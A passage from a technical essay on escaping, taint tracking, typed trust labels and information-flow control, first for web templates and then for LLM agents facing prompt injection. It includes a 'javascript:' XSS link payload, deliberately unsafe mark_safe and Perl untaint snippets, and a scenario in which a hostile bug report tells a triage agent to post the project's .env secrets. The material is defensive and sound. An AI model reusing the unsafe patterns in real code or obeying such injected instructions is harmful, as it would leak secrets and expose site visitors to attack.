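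delroth (2016), in *Autoescaping disabled by default is a dangerous default*, describes the consequences. He learned about the setting only when someone reported an XSS hole in his own software. Jinja2's syntax was modeled on Django's, so people who switched from Django could easily assume that it escaped values too. He found a programming textbook that recommended Jinja2 for websites and left escaping off, and most of the GitHub projects he sampled did not turn it on.

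The maintainers replied that Jinja2 produces many kinds of text besides HTML. They thought most people used it through Flask, a web framework built on Jinja2 that turns escaping on for HTML templates. Flask therefore supplied the safe default, but developers who used Jinja2 directly had to turn escaping on themselves. One maintainer declined to change the default because it would break everybody's code, though he welcomed better documentation.

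The default was still causing security holes in November 2017. Few people understood the danger better than Willison, whose design Django had adopted ten years earlier, but he had missed an opt-in setting and had to fix XSS holes in Datasette, his tool for publishing data. He cited delroth's complaint in the change and expected no real harm because Datasette had no logins to steal.

### When the escaper doesn't fit the context

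The template at the start of this section has a hole that Django's default does not close. Suppose escaping is on and an attacker enters this as their website:

```
javascript:stealLogin()
```

HTML escaping changes angle brackets, ampersands and quotation marks. The attacker's text has none of these, so the escaper returns it unchanged and the template produces a normal-looking link. When a visitor clicks the link, the browser runs the rest of the address as a script because it begins with `javascript:`. The escaper worked as designed, but it was the wrong one for an address.

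The right treatment depends on where the value lands.

| Position of the value | Example | Weakness if the template only escapes HTML | Suitable treatment |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary text | `<h2>{{ title }}</h2>` | None | HTML escaping |
| Attribute without quotation marks | `<input value={{ answer }}>` | A space ends the value, and the rest can become new attributes | Add quotation marks, then escape |
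| Start of an address | `<a href="{{ website }}">` | The value can begin with `javascript:` | Allow only known types of address, such as `https`, then escape |
| Number in a script | `var id = {{ id }};` | The value can be code | Allow only simple values such as numbers |

Django's developers knew about this. In the 2007 discussion, Ned Batchelder posted examples of values inside scripts and said he couldn't work out how to protect one of them. Tredinnick answered that automatic escaping in scripts was "a pretty doomed exercise" and that authors would have to understand their own code there.

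Two years later, Google announced Auto-Escape, a template feature that chose the escaper by context. The announcement includes a short template with four values that each need different escaping: a color in a style setting, a username in ordinary text, an account address in a link, and a number in a script. Auto-Escape reads the HTML around each value to determine its position, then applies the matching escaper.

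It could not handle templates with branches and loops, according to *Context-Sensitive Auto-Sanitization in Web Templating Languages Using Type Qualifiers* (Samuel, Saxena and Song, 2011). The paper's example is a template that builds the address of an image. If the person has a name, the template puts the attacker's value after a question mark, near the end of the address. If not, the value becomes the entire address and could begin with `javascript:`. The variable therefore needs a different escaper on each path.

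Their solution uses type qualifiers, extra labels that a compiler attaches to the type of each value. Every untrusted string starts as unsafe. A string becomes printable only when it has a qualifier naming the context where it is safe, such as ordinary text or the start of an address. The compiler reads the fixed HTML to find the context at each output point, follows every branch, and works out which qualifier each string needs. It then inserts the escaper that converts the string to that qualifier. If other templates call a template from two contexts, the compiler makes a separate copy for each.

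Samuel and colleagues built this into Closure Templates, which Google used for Gmail and Google Docs, and ran it on 1,035 existing templates. After copying, the templates had 1,348 points where untrusted text reached a page. In 1.3 seconds, the compiler found a suitable escaper for all of them without any change to the templates. Plain HTML escaping would have been enough at 982 points, but a default like Django's would have applied the wrong escaper at the other 366, more than a quarter of the total.

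Choosing an escaper by context was about as fast as using the same escaper everywhere. In three browsers the templates ran 3% to 9.6% slower than with no escaping, and on a Java server the difference was too small to measure. Working out the context each time a page was built made the templates 79% to 510% slower.

Google had already audited these templates, and its developers had placed escapers by hand. The compiler chose the same escaper at all but 21 points, where the developers had picked one that was stricter than necessary, so the experiment uncovered no vulnerabilities. It does show that a compiler can match careful, well-funded reviewers, which most projects lack.

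The guarantee depends on a correct escaper for every context and on all browsers parsing the HTML in the same way. It doesn't cover other code that puts the finished output somewhere unexpected.

### Did the new defaults prevent vulnerabilities?

No study followed a large group of applications before and after the change, so the evidence is indirect. Finifter and Wagner came closest to a controlled comparison in *Exploring the Relationship Between Web Application Development Tools and Security*. They examined the work of nine professional teams that had each built the same small social website in 30 hours for a programming contest. Three teams used Java, three used Perl and three used PHP. One of the researchers reviewed all the code by hand and ran an automated attack tool. Together, the two methods found 91 vulnerabilities.

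The researchers sorted framework protections into four levels. An always-on protection cannot be removed without abandoning the framework, and an opt-out protection works until a developer disables it. A developer has to turn on an opt-in protection once for the whole application and call a manual protection every time it is needed.

Manual protections in the teams' own frameworks would have prevented 37 of the vulnerabilities. In 30 cases, the team had used the relevant protection correctly elsewhere in the same application, so its developers knew about the danger and the remedy but still missed a place. That fits SmileyChris's view of developers better than Powell's advice to be more careful.

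Automatic protection did better, though the evidence is thin. All seven teams with automatic support for session management, which keeps track of who is logged in, got it right, while both teams without it got it wrong. Some of the seven had only opt-in support, so turning on one setting was enough for them. Opt-in support wasn't enough for password storage, because several teams never turned on the secure option their frameworks offered.

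The study also covered cross-site request forgery, in which another website makes a visitor's browser send unwanted requests. Seven teams had no framework protection against it, and all seven were vulnerable. The other two were safe, but one had only manual protection, so this result is stronger evidence for making protection available than for making it automatic.

Finifter and Wagner could not test automatic escaping, because none of the teams' frameworks had it. They also ran 19 statistical tests and warned that one or two of their three significant results might be due to chance. The finding about the 30 vulnerabilities does not depend on those tests and is probably the most useful one for judging defaults.

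Steinhauser and Tůma looked for escaping errors that remained after a decade of automatic escaping in Django. They studied eight large, actively maintained applications totaling more than half a million lines of code. Their tool recorded every escaper applied to a piece of outside text, then parsed the finished page as a browser would to check whether those escapers suited the text's position.

| Result | Number of cases |
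|---|---|
| All cases the tool examined | 661 |
| Incorrect treatment | 85 |
| No escaping at all | 7 |
| HTML escaping in an address | 68 |
| HTML escaping in another unsuitable position | 10 |

Only about 1% of the cases had no escaping, as one would expect if the default had mostly solved the problem of forgotten calls. The study has no comparison group of applications without the default, so it can't show how many more such cases there would have been without it. Nearly all the remaining errors came from escaping for the wrong context. Many of the errors in addresses were hard to exploit, but the researchers managed to run their own script in at least 26 of the 85 cases, across seven of the eight applications.

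These results support Anderson's warning about a false sense of security. The researchers also tried three existing scanning tools, which found none of the 78 cases with the wrong escaper. Scanners treat a page with some escaping as protected, and human reviewers probably do too.

Developers also made this kind of error when they placed escapers by hand. *ScriptGard*, a 2011 study of a commercial application with more than 400,000 lines of code, found manually placed escapers that did not fit their context. Automatic HTML escaping removed much of the risk of forgetting an escaper, but developers still had to choose the right one. Context-aware systems such as Auto-Escape then addressed that problem too.

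### Misplaced safe marks

A safe mark is a trust override, and it can be wrong. The simplest misuse is to mark too much:

```
mark_safe("<b>" + title + "</b>")
```

The developer only wants the title in bold and knows the tags are harmless. But `mark_safe` applies to the whole string, including whatever the attacker put in the title. The developer should have escaped the title before joining it to the tags.

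Samuel and Saxena describe how ordinary maintenance removes manual escaping calls that are still needed. A template escapes a person's name, and then another team starts to use it with names that already contain safe formatting. Someone complains that tags appear on the page. A developer checks that the new names are clean, removes the escaping call and closes the complaint, without noticing that the older code still passes in raw text. Users report visible tags but rarely report vulnerabilities they can't see, so a project tends to lose escaping calls over the years. Developers face the same temptation with automatic escaping, because adding `mark_safe` also makes the tags disappear.

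A value that was safe when a developer exempted it from escaping could become dangerous later. In two of the applications Steinhauser and Tůma studied, a value from the database reached the page unescaped. Nobody could exploit these values at the time because they were either fixed in the program or cleaned before storage. If a plugin later let users edit one of them, the page would become vulnerable, and the plugin's author would have no reason to look at the template.

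Framework developers made similar mistakes. In *Rails XSS protection and helpers*, a programmer reported that a Rails function for labeling form fields returned its input unescaped but marked as safe. Koziarski confirmed the bug. In *Potential XSS Vulnerability in Ruby on Rails Applications*, aaronp (2011) announced a wider problem, in which certain operations could insert a user's text into a safe string without removing the safe mark. Django's rule for filters guards against this by removing the mark unless someone has declared that the output is still safe.

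In the 2007 Django discussion, Tom Tobin asked what a "safe" string was safe from, since Django templates produce emails, data files and JavaScript as well as HTML. He wanted the name to mention HTML. SafeHtml types, which let a compiler check declarations that a string is safe, and the browser feature Trusted Types later included the intended use in the label. An endorsement in an agent framework also needs to specify its intended use, because text that a maintainer has approved for a documentation page may still be dangerous in a shell command.

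In Rails, output could also go unescaped without an override, because the default applied only to ERB, the template system that came with Rails, and many developers used others. In *XSS and Alternate Template Engines*, Yehuda Katz complained that people were being told they had protection by default while any other template system would "drive a big truck" through it. He suggested a warning for developers whose template system did not escape.

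Even so, overrides are easier to review than omissions. A search for `mark_safe` or Rails's `raw` finds places where a developer chose to bypass escaping, and a reviewer can check each one. With opt-in escaping, the reviewer has to find places where the escaping call is missing. Samuel and Saxena made searching for overrides a goal of their design so that any exception would be easy to audit.

### Language models have no escaping function

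Default escaping works because a correct escaper makes text harmless to an HTML parser, the part of a browser that turns a page's text into a structure of headings, links and scripts. Samuel and Saxena define this precisely. Take a template and fill every gap with a harmless string such as `zzz`. Parse the result to get a tree of elements. Then fill the gaps with any other values and parse again:

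```
shape(parse(T(values))) = shape(parse(T("zzz")))
```

The template is safe in this respect if the two trees have the same shape for every possible value and every path through the template. An attacker can then change the words inside a heading but cannot add a script or close a tag early. Testing every value is impossible, but an engineer can prove the property from the rules of HTML, because they specify which characters start a tag. Real escapers have bugs, and browsers sometimes disagree about unusual HTML, but in each case there is a correct answer for developers to work toward.

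None of this carries over to a language model. The model processes instructions and data as one sequence of tokens, so an escaper has no tree structure to preserve and no fixed set of characters to replace.

A browser can also display text without executing it, so `&lt;script&gt;` appears on the screen as a tag. The triage agent, however, has to interpret an issue to summarize it, and whatever it interprets can influence what it does next. A framework that scrambled the text enough to make the attacker's request unreadable to the model would make the bug report unreadable too.

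Training makes models more likely to ignore planted instructions, but the low failure rates that developers report are averages over the attacks they tried. A correct escaper works for every input, including attacks nobody has thought of. Researchers know of no way to transform arbitrary text that would give a language model the same guarantee and keep the text useful.

Labeling everything untrusted doesn't by itself protect an agent the way escaping protects a web page. Once Django has escaped an issue title for a heading, the browser displays it as text, no matter who wrote it. When an agent framework labels the same title untrusted, the model still reads the same words and may still call `post_comment` with the contents of `.env`. The label protects the project only if the code that runs `post_comment` checks it and blocks the call.

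Refusing is also more disruptive than escaping. An escaped title looks exactly as its author typed it, so most developers have no reason to turn escaping off. But refusing a comment leaves the agent's job unfinished, which gives the developer a strong reason to look for an override.

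## What do trust labels enforced by types add?

Automatic escaping protects only text that passes through a template. Programs also pass outside text to shells, databases and browser functions, which may run it as code. To cover these routes, Perl and Ruby attached a taint flag to outside text while a program ran, but the flags were easy to lose and Ruby eventually dropped them. Google instead put the label in the text's type, so a program that passes unlabeled text to a dangerous function does not compile. An agent framework could similarly use types to ensure that every tool result has a label, but types cannot track how the text influences a model's output.

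### Perl's taint flag

A programmer turns on Perl's taint mode with the `-T` switch. According to SEI, a software research institute at Carnegie Mellon University, every value then has a flag that shows whether it is tainted. The flag belongs to the value rather than the variable, so copying the value also copies the flag. If a tainted value reaches a dangerous operation, such as running a shell command with `system()`, Perl stops the program with a fatal error.

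Perl's security manual describes a propagation rule under which an expression's whole result is tainted if any value in it is tainted. This sometimes flags harmless text, but it takes less work than testing every argument of every operator. An agent's context label follows much the same rule, applied to a whole run instead of one expression.

Programs do sometimes need to act on outside text, so programmers need a way to clear the flag. In Perl, the usual way is to match the text against a regular expression, a pattern that describes which characters may appear, and keep the part that the pattern captured. The trouble is that any pattern will do:

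```perl
my $name = <STDIN>;              # typed by a stranger, so tainted
unlink $name;                    # fatal error instead of deleting the file
my ($copy) = $name =~ /^(.*)$/;  # captures the whole line
unlink $copy;                    # allowed
```

The pattern in the third line matches any text. Without the second line, this program would delete whatever file the stranger named. The manual advises programmers to think about their patterns and not untaint data blindly, but Perl cannot enforce that advice. A programmer may also clear the flag by accident, for example by using a pattern to split a line into fields. Perl's *re* documentation describes an opt-in setting that keeps captured text tainted, for patterns that aren't meant as safety checks, but it helps only programmers who already know about the problem.

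The add-on module *Taint::Util* has an `untaint` function that clears the flag without a pattern match, and its documentation shows a single call clearing every environment variable. Reviewers can search for `untaint` as they can for Django's `mark_safe`, so its uses are easier to find than pattern matches that clear the flag, even though it looks more reckless. Ordinary Perl programs use pattern matches throughout, which makes the ones that clear the flag hard to pick out.

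The flag also doesn't distinguish between uses, so a pattern that makes text safe to use as a file name clears it for shell commands too, even if the text is still dangerous there.

### Why Ruby removed its taint flag

Ruby had a similar flag, and a variable called `$SAFE` set how strictly the language enforced it. At the default setting, Ruby did not check the flag. Saeloun's *Ruby 2.7 removes taint checking mechanism* (2020) says that programmers used taint checks extensively in the days of CGI, an early way of running programs on web servers. Most later input libraries didn't support them, including Rack, which connects Ruby applications to web servers, so text from visitors could arrive without a flag and pass as trusted. Researchers also found several vulnerabilities in the mechanism itself.

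In August 2019, Naruse proposed removing the mechanism because it took too much work to maintain for the benefit it brought (*Remove $SAFE, taint and trust*, 2019). Endoh, another Ruby developer, added that hardly anyone seemed to use `$SAFE`. The maintenance work extended well beyond the core language. To remove the flag, Evans had to change all the libraries that came with Ruby, including its package manager and JSON parser.

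The taint flag also interfered with work unrelated to security. Ruby has an operator that saves memory by storing identical strings only once, and it skipped tainted strings. Text from a configuration file was tainted, so developers had to untaint it before the operator would work on it. A contributor proposed that the operator clear the flag itself, on the grounds that anyone who keeps a string in memory long-term implicitly trusts it. An agent framework could lose labels the same way if a developer removes them to shorten a conversation.

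In Ruby 2.7, the methods for setting and clearing the flag stopped doing anything. Using `$SAFE` always produced a warning, but calling the taint methods produced one only in verbose mode. A check written to refuse tainted strings still ran after the upgrade but let every string through. According to *Feature #16131*, Ruby's developers wanted to keep the empty methods for several versions because most library authors also had to support older versions of Ruby.

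### Values that only reviewed code can create

A type specifies what sort of value a variable holds, and the compiler rejects a program that passes text to a function that takes a number. Google's security engineers applied the same check to trust. *Securing the Tangled Web* (Kern, 2014) describes how a function that puts HTML on a page accepts a `SafeHtml` value and rejects an ordinary string. Every ordinary string is therefore treated as potentially untrusted, wherever it came from, and input libraries don't have to mark data as untrusted.

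Wang, Bangert and Kern, in *If It’s Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (2021), describe the version that Google later applied to all its JavaScript. The compiler also bans the browser's original functions, since developers could otherwise go around the safe ones. Applied to the web page that shows the triage project's issues, the rules work like this:

```ts
const title: string = issue.title;   // chosen by whoever filed the issue

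document.write(title);                                  // error: banned function
safeDocumentWrite(document, title);                     // error: string is not SafeHtml
safeDocumentWrite(document, SafeHtml.sanitize(title));  // compiles

const home = SafeUrl.fromLiteral('https://example.com');
safeSetLocationHref(window.location, home);             // compiles
safeDocumentWrite(document, home);                      // error: SafeUrl is not SafeHtml
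```

The last line fails because each type marks a value as safe for a particular use. Google has six such types, and some of the distinctions between them are subtle. `SafeUrl` means that a browser can follow the address without running an attacker's script, which may well be true of a link to a stranger's blog. `TrustedResourceUrl` means that the page can safely load code from the address, which would be unsafe for the same blog.

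Developers can create a safe value in four ways.

| Method | Why the value should be safe | Limitation |
|---|---|---|
| From text written in the program | An attacker cannot change it | A developer can still write in the address of an untrustworthy site |
| With a sanitizer | The sanitizer removes dangerous parts | It also removes legitimate scripts, because it can't tell them apart |
| From a strict template | The template picks an escaper for each position and allows no exceptions | It suits only content that fits a template |
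| With an unchecked conversion | A security engineer has reviewed the code around it | The conversion itself accepts any string |

The compiler checks that every `SafeHtml` value came from code that experts were supposed to review. It can't check whether a sanitizer removes every dangerous script, so experts have to establish that by reading and testing the sanitizer. TypeScript normally accepts any object with the right fields, whatever its type is called, so Google's types include a private field that other code cannot supply. This prevents developers from creating a lookalike by accident.

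### What reviewers no longer have to read

Without these types, a reviewer has to find every place where a program passes text to a dangerous function and trace each value back to its origin. Kern's example is a photo-sharing site that shows visitors the titles of other people's albums. The reviewer has to trace a title from the browser back through a server and a database to the user who typed it. The same database holds addresses that the site's staff configured, so the reviewer can't assume that all stored text is safe or that all of it is dangerous. A large application may have thousands of such paths, and each change can add another.

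With types, the reviewer doesn't need to trace data that ends up in a safe function, because a mistake along the way produces either a compiler error or harmless output. Suppose the photo site lets users write a formatted description of themselves. The developers change that field from a string to `SafeHtml`, and the compiler then requires the new type at every step back to the server code that creates the value. That code sanitizes the description and then uses an unchecked conversion to turn it into `SafeHtml`. Within the application, only the small package containing this code needs a security review. Experts also have to review the template system and the safe functions, but many applications share those.

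The unchecked conversion is the weak point, since any developer could use it to suppress compiler errors. Google's build system therefore allowed only approved packages to call it. In the later JavaScript version, the compiler bans the conversion, along with other functions, unless a security engineer has added the calling file to a central exemption list. The engineer first checks that no safe function could do the job, then that the code is simple enough to judge with confidence. Django developers, by contrast, can add `mark_safe` to get rid of stray tags without anyone else's approval.

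A determined developer can still bypass the types, for example by telling the TypeScript compiler to treat the browser's address object as a plain object with a text field, then assigning a dangerous address to that field. Wang and colleagues, who aimed to prevent accidents, accept this because the code looks strange enough for a reviewer to notice.

### How Google moved its existing code

Google first applied the JavaScript checks to selected projects that opted in. In early 2018, it made them mandatory across the company, which has more than a million JavaScript files. Google could not stop all other work to repair old code, so whenever the security team banned another function, it automatically exempted the files that already used that function. Those files still compiled, but new code had to follow the rule.

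Teams then reduced the exemptions by rewriting old code in projects with a history of vulnerabilities, often with a tool that could make the same correction in many files. If developers were likely to replace the code soon anyway, teams waited for them to do so. By the end of 2020, fewer than 1% of files were exempt from any check, even though the list of banned functions had grown.

The compiler's error messages suggested a correction and explained how to ask questions. After a company-wide campaign in October 2018, the security team received about one question a week, while developers made roughly 10,000 JavaScript changes a week. Requests for exemptions averaged fewer than eight a week over five months that included the campaign. Reviewers rejected unnecessary requests and pointed the developers to a suitable safe function. According to *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* (Kern,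 2024), a small team of security engineers maintains the safe libraries and checks, and supports many thousands of web developers.

Other organizations would probably find the change harder. Wang and colleagues say that having one shared code repository, compulsory code review and the same build tools everywhere helped. A small open-source project can turn on the checks but may have nobody qualified to judge exemption requests.

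### Did vulnerabilities fall?

Google's engineers have published counts for three applications.

| Application | XSS bugs before | XSS bugs later |
|---|---|---|
| Large application with more than 1,000 templates | 31 in 2012 | 4 in the year to mid-2014, after migration |
| Second large application | 21 in 2012 | 9 in the year to mid-2014, with migration unfinished |
| Product with a few dozen browser-code developers | 10 in the year before adoption | 2 during the year of adoption, 1 in the year after |

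The third row counts only DOM-based XSS, in which a script already running in the page passes outside text to a dangerous browser function. None of these comparisons had a control group. Kern calls the 2014 figures anecdotal, because training or a change in an application's size could also affect the number of bugs. The product in the third row belonged to an especially willing team, which may have been more careful in other ways.

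A company-wide comparison is more persuasive. From 2018, DOM-based XSS made up a shrinking share of the serious vulnerabilities that outside researchers reported to Google. A growing share of the DOM-based XSS bugs they found was in old code that did not use the safe functions, even though the amount of such code was falling. This is the pattern one would expect if the rules worked, because new code had to compile under them. General improvements, such as better training, would also have helped new code, so they can't be ruled out.

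*Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* reports later and stronger figures. Large applications such as Gmail used to have tens of XSS vulnerabilities each per year. Ten years later, all the applications built on Google's protected frameworks had a low single-digit number combined. Nobody had ever reported one in the web version of Google Photos. Some of the remaining risk came from old components that were still exempt.

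Google used the same method against SQL injection. Its internal database functions accept a `TrustedSqlString`, which developers can build only from trusted pieces such as text in the program or a trusted configuration file. The type has no function for appending an arbitrary string. Developers have to pass visitors' text separately, as a parameter that the database never interprets as a command. Kern describes SQL injection as essentially a solved problem in Google's internal code.

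All these numbers come from the company that designed the method. Still, the improvement doesn't seem to reflect a general decline in XSS. Helme reports in *XSS Ranked #1 Top Threat of 2025 by MITRE and CISA* that XSS topped a US list of dangerous software weaknesses, with about twice as many recorded vulnerabilities as the next entry.

### Trusted Types in the browser

Compile-time checks don't cover code that never goes through the compiler, such as a script from another company. Google therefore proposed Trusted Types, a web standard that moves the check into the browser. A site turns it on by sending this instruction with a page:

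```
Content-Security-Policy: require-trusted-types-for 'script'
```

The browser then refuses plain strings at dangerous functions. Developers define a policy, which is a named function that turns strings into typed values:

```js
const policy = trustedTypes.createPolicy('issues', {
  createHTML: text => sanitize(text)
});

box.innerHTML = issue.title;                     // error when this line runs
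box.innerHTML = policy.createHTML(issue.title);  // accepted
```

The site can also list the names of permitted policies, which makes it harder for a forgotten script to add its own. As with an unchecked conversion, the protection depends on the policy's code. If `createHTML` returned its input unchanged, the browser would accept the result, and the page would be as vulnerable as before. Google reports that Trusted Types reduced the code needing review from whole applications, with more than 60 kinds of dangerous function, to a single function.

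Google estimated from past bug reports that Trusted Types could prevent at least 61% of the DOM-based XSS that its automated code analysis had missed. By then, it had moved 130 services to Trusted Types. PortSwigger's *Internal deployment has nullified elusive, complex threat since 2019* reports that Google's engineers found no DOM-based XSS afterward in a group of migrated applications that included Contacts and My Activity. By August 2025, Google had extended Trusted Types and a related protection to hundreds of products, and it still used compile-time checks.

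A compiler reports an error to the developer, but the browser check fails only when a visitor's browser reaches the line, and the page may then stop working. The standard therefore has a report-only mode, which a site uses by sending its policy in the `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only` header. The browser then lets the old code run and sends the site a report of each violation, so developers can fix the reported code before they turn on enforcement. This mode finds only code that visitors run, so a rarely used page may still break later.

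Limited browser support was another obstacle for years. URIports' *Beyond script-src* dates support in Chrome and Edge to May 2020 and in Safari to September 2025. Firefox added support in version 148, in February 2026. The standard had changed since Chrome's early implementation, so the two no longer fully matched. In *Intent to ship*, Frédéric Wang (2025) told Firefox developers that Chrome's developers planned to close the gap in February 2026.

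Firefox 148 also supports `setHTML()`, a built-in function that sanitizes HTML before adding it to a page. Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026) notes that a strict policy can allow this function and block the unsafe ones. Many sites would then not need to write their own policy function, which removes one place for mistakes.

Few sites use Trusted Types so far. *Top 1 Million Analysis June 2026* (Helme, 2026) surveyed the home pages of a million popular sites, of which 819,002 responded. About 170,000 had a content security policy, and only 318 of those policies required Trusted Types. The survey would miss a site that protects only its account or payment pages. By contrast, HTTP Archive's 2025 survey, *Security*, found the same Trusted Types policy in 12% of the policy headers on mobile pages. All the copies send reports to the same Android-related address, which suggests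 a single origin rather than thousands of separate decisions, though *Security* could not explain it.

Helme's survey also shows how much faster a default spreads than an opt-in feature. A header that turns on network error reporting in browsers was on about 289,000 sites, roughly 97% of them because Cloudflare, a company that delivers web pages for other sites, adds it automatically. The comparison somewhat overstates the advantage of defaults, since Trusted Types, unlike error reporting, can break a page. Difficulty of use also matters. *Trust Me If You Can* (Roth, Gröber and colleagues, 2024), which interviewed 13 web developers and gave them a coding task, identified key weaknesses in the design and documentation of Trusted Types.

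### Labeled tool results

An agent framework could borrow the part of this design that makes labels compulsory. Suppose that the triage agent's framework had a type called `Labeled`, which holds a piece of text with its integrity and confidentiality labels, and that tools and prompts accepted nothing else:

```ts
function readIssue(id: number): Labeled {
  return download(id);                // error: string is not Labeled
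}

function readIssue(id: number): Labeled {
  return untrusted(download(id));     // compiles
}

prompt.add(issue.authorName);             // error: string is not Labeled
prompt.add(untrusted(issue.authorName));  // compiles
```

If a type requires a trust label, code that omits the label doesn't compile, so nobody has to decide what a missing label means. This requirement would have caught the issue title in Cline's template, the unwrapped Grok results in OpenClaw and the folder name in OpenClaw's system prompt. A type could also enforce the origin tags that Suwansathit and colleagues proposed for OpenClaw.

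A developer could still write `trusted(download(id))` to make the error go away. To prevent this, the framework would have to allow `trusted` only in a short list of approved files, as Google does with unchecked conversions. Reviewers could then read that list instead of every tool and template.

Some text reaches an agent without passing through code that the project compiles. When another company's tool server returns results, the framework's connection code has to label them, preferably in one shared function that marks them as untrusted. Text loaded from a notes file is an ordinary string, whatever type it had when the agent saved it, so the framework must store the label with the text. Python, a common language for agent frameworks, doesn't enforce type declarations when a program runs, so a Python framework would need to check the type again when text enters the prompt, much as a browser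 does with Trusted Types.

Types can also protect a sink if code can check the value without knowing its origin. For example, `write_file` might accept only a `DocsPath`, whose constructor rejects any location outside the documentation folder. That would stop an injected instruction from changing the build configuration, though a false sentence could still enter the documentation. No constructor could do for the text of a public comment what `SafeHtml.sanitize` does for HTML, because whether the comment reveals a secret depends on where its contents came from.

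The larger gap opens when the framework calls the model:

```ts
const reply: string = await model.run(prompt);
postComment(reply);              // error: string is not Labeled
```

The compiler correctly requires a label for the reply, but nothing in the reply shows which parts of the prompt influenced it. If the framework always labeled replies as trusted, that would include replies influenced by an attacker's instructions. If it always labeled them as untrusted, a strict `postComment` would reject even a reply based entirely on the project's own files. A more useful label depends on what the model has read, which can't be determined at compile time because the model chooses its tools during the run. The type can guarantee that a label is present, but the framework has to compute and check the label's value at runtime.

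Labels on text also don't track what influenced the model's choice of action. Suppose `postComment` accepts a fixed sentence from the program, such as "Closed as a duplicate." The sentence is trusted, so the call compiles, but text in a hostile issue may have led the model to post it under a serious bug report. Perl's taint flag has the same limitation. If a program tests a tainted value and then picks one of two fixed strings, the chosen string is untainted even though the tainted value determined the choice.

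## How does information-flow control label everything an agent reads?

Information-flow control (IFC) lets a framework compute the labels that types can't determine in advance, including the label for a model's reply. Dorothy Denning published the underlying mathematics for ordinary programs in 1976. In an agent, IFC can block a dangerous tool call no matter how persuasive the attacker's text is, if the framework labeled that text correctly.

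### The label lattice

IFC needs an order on its labels. The notation `a ⊑ b` means that content labeled `a` may flow to a place labeled `b`, because `b` is at least as restrictive. For integrity, trusted ⊑ untrusted, so a trusted sentence may go into an untrusted document, but an untrusted sentence may not go into a trusted one. For confidentiality, public ⊑ private.

The triage agent needs both kinds of label, so each piece of content gets a pair. Content may flow upward in this diagram:

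```
              (untrusted, private)
               /                \
  (trusted, private)      (untrusted, public)
               \                /
               (trusted, public)
```

Neither of the two labels in the middle ranks above the other, because the `.env` file is more secret than a stranger's bug report but also more trustworthy.

When the model reads several pieces of content, the framework combines their labels with an operation called the join, written `⊔`. The join of two labels is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both:

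```
trusted ⊔ untrusted = untrusted
public ⊔ private = private
(trusted, private) ⊔ (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, private)
```

A lattice is an ordered set in which every two elements have a least upper bound, called the join, and a greatest lower bound, but agents use only the join.

The context label is a running join. If `c₀` is the label of the developer's instructions and the user's request, and `ℓₙ` is the label of the nth message after that, then:

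```
cₙ = cₙ₋₁ ⊔ ℓₙ
```

A join is never less restrictive than either of its inputs, so the context label can only stay the same or become more restrictive. Reading ten trusted files after one hostile issue doesn't make the context trusted again. With the four labels above, the context label can change at most twice in a run, once when the agent reads something untrusted and once when it reads something private.

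### Reader sets

If a confidentiality label is a list of permitted readers, the join has to keep only the people who appear on every list. Costa and colleagues give the example of one document that A, B and C may read and another that B, C and D may read. A summary of both could reveal something from either, so only people with permission for both documents may see it:

```
{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}
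```

The join is therefore an intersection, and a label becomes more restrictive as its list of readers gets shorter.

Microsoft shows how this prevents a leak even when there is no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer some emails. One from Priya previews the quarterly sales, and another is from Marco, who is curious about the sales but not yet allowed to know them. After the agent reads both, its reply has the label {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent may not send it to Marco on its own. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the label would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could send the reply.

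An integrity label can list everyone who could have written the content, and the join of two labels is the union of their lists. If A, B and C could have edited one document and B, C and D another, any of the four could have influenced a summary of both. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) uses labels of this kind to record which sources, such as a particular website, influenced the data.

### The triage agent reads a malicious issue

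The framework also needs a rule for each tool. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, describe two rules that they consider sufficient for most practical cases. Under the trusted-action rule, a call may proceed only if the model decided on it in a trusted context. Under the permitted-flow rule, a call may send data only to people who are allowed to read it. For the triage agent, this gives:

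| Tool | Rule |
|---|---|
| `read_issue`, `read_file` | Always allowed |
| `write_file` | Trusted action |
| `post_comment` | Trusted action or permitted flow |

Suppose a maintainer asks the agent to handle new issues on a public repository, and the first is the fake macOS bug report with instructions to post the contents of `.env`.

| Step | Label of the new content | Context label afterward | Decision |
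|---|---|---|---|
| The run starts with the developer's instructions and the maintainer's request | (trusted, public) | (trusted, public) | None needed |
| `read_issue` returns the bug report | (untrusted, public) | (untrusted, public) | Allowed |
| `read_file` returns `.env` | (trusted, private) | (untrusted, private) | Allowed |
| The model requests `post_comment` with the secrets | No new content | (untrusted, private) | Refused |

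The last call fails both rules because the context is untrusted and anyone on the internet could read a comment based on private data. The join would have been the same if the agent had read `.env` before the issue.

The framework would have allowed an ordinary reply. If the agent has only called `read_issue`, the context is untrusted but public, so a public comment reveals nothing private and satisfies the permitted-flow rule. The agent can therefore still answer bug reports from strangers. The rule for `write_file` is stricter. Once the agent has read the issue, the framework refuses every change to a file, even to fix a typo that an honest user pointed out.

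The attack resembles one that researchers demonstrated against coding assistants connected to GitHub. According to Microsoft, the attacker opened an issue in a public repository asking for information from a private one. An agent working for someone with access to both could then copy the private data into a public comment. The labels stop an agent from mixing public and private repositories in this way, but an agent that works only on public repositories, or only on private ones, can finish without interruption.

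### The refusal doesn't depend on the model

The framework blocked the attack without anyone having to notice it. The check at `post_comment` uses the context label and the list of people who can see the comment, and the wording of the issue affects neither. The label would be the same if the attacker had written the footer in another language, encoded it or left it out. The framework will refuse the call even if the model treats the request as authorized by a maintainer. Disguising the password or splitting it across several comments doesn't help, because every comment gets the label of the whole context.

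Kim and colleagues tested this independence in Flowsh, which applies IFC to an agent's shell commands. They assumed that the attacker fully controls the model's output once an injection has succeeded. None of their attacks achieved its goal. Unlike the low failure rates that model developers publish, this result doesn't depend on how well the model resists injections.

The user's intent also doesn't affect the check. If an honest user reports a configuration problem and the agent reads `.env` to diagnose it, the framework blocks the reply, even if the reply contains no secrets.

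### The formal model of FIDES

Costa and colleagues turned these ideas into a mathematical model and an agent called FIDES. In their model, the planner is a piece of ordinary code that keeps the conversation and decides what to do with each new message. It can query the language model, call a tool or finish. A separate loop carries out the planner's choice and keeps track of the labels. In simplified form:

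```
if the planner wants to query the model:
    reply = model(conversation)
    label(reply) = label(conversation)

if the planner wants to call tool f with arguments a₁ … aₙ:
    if the policy engine rejects the call: stop
    result = f(a₁ … aₙ)
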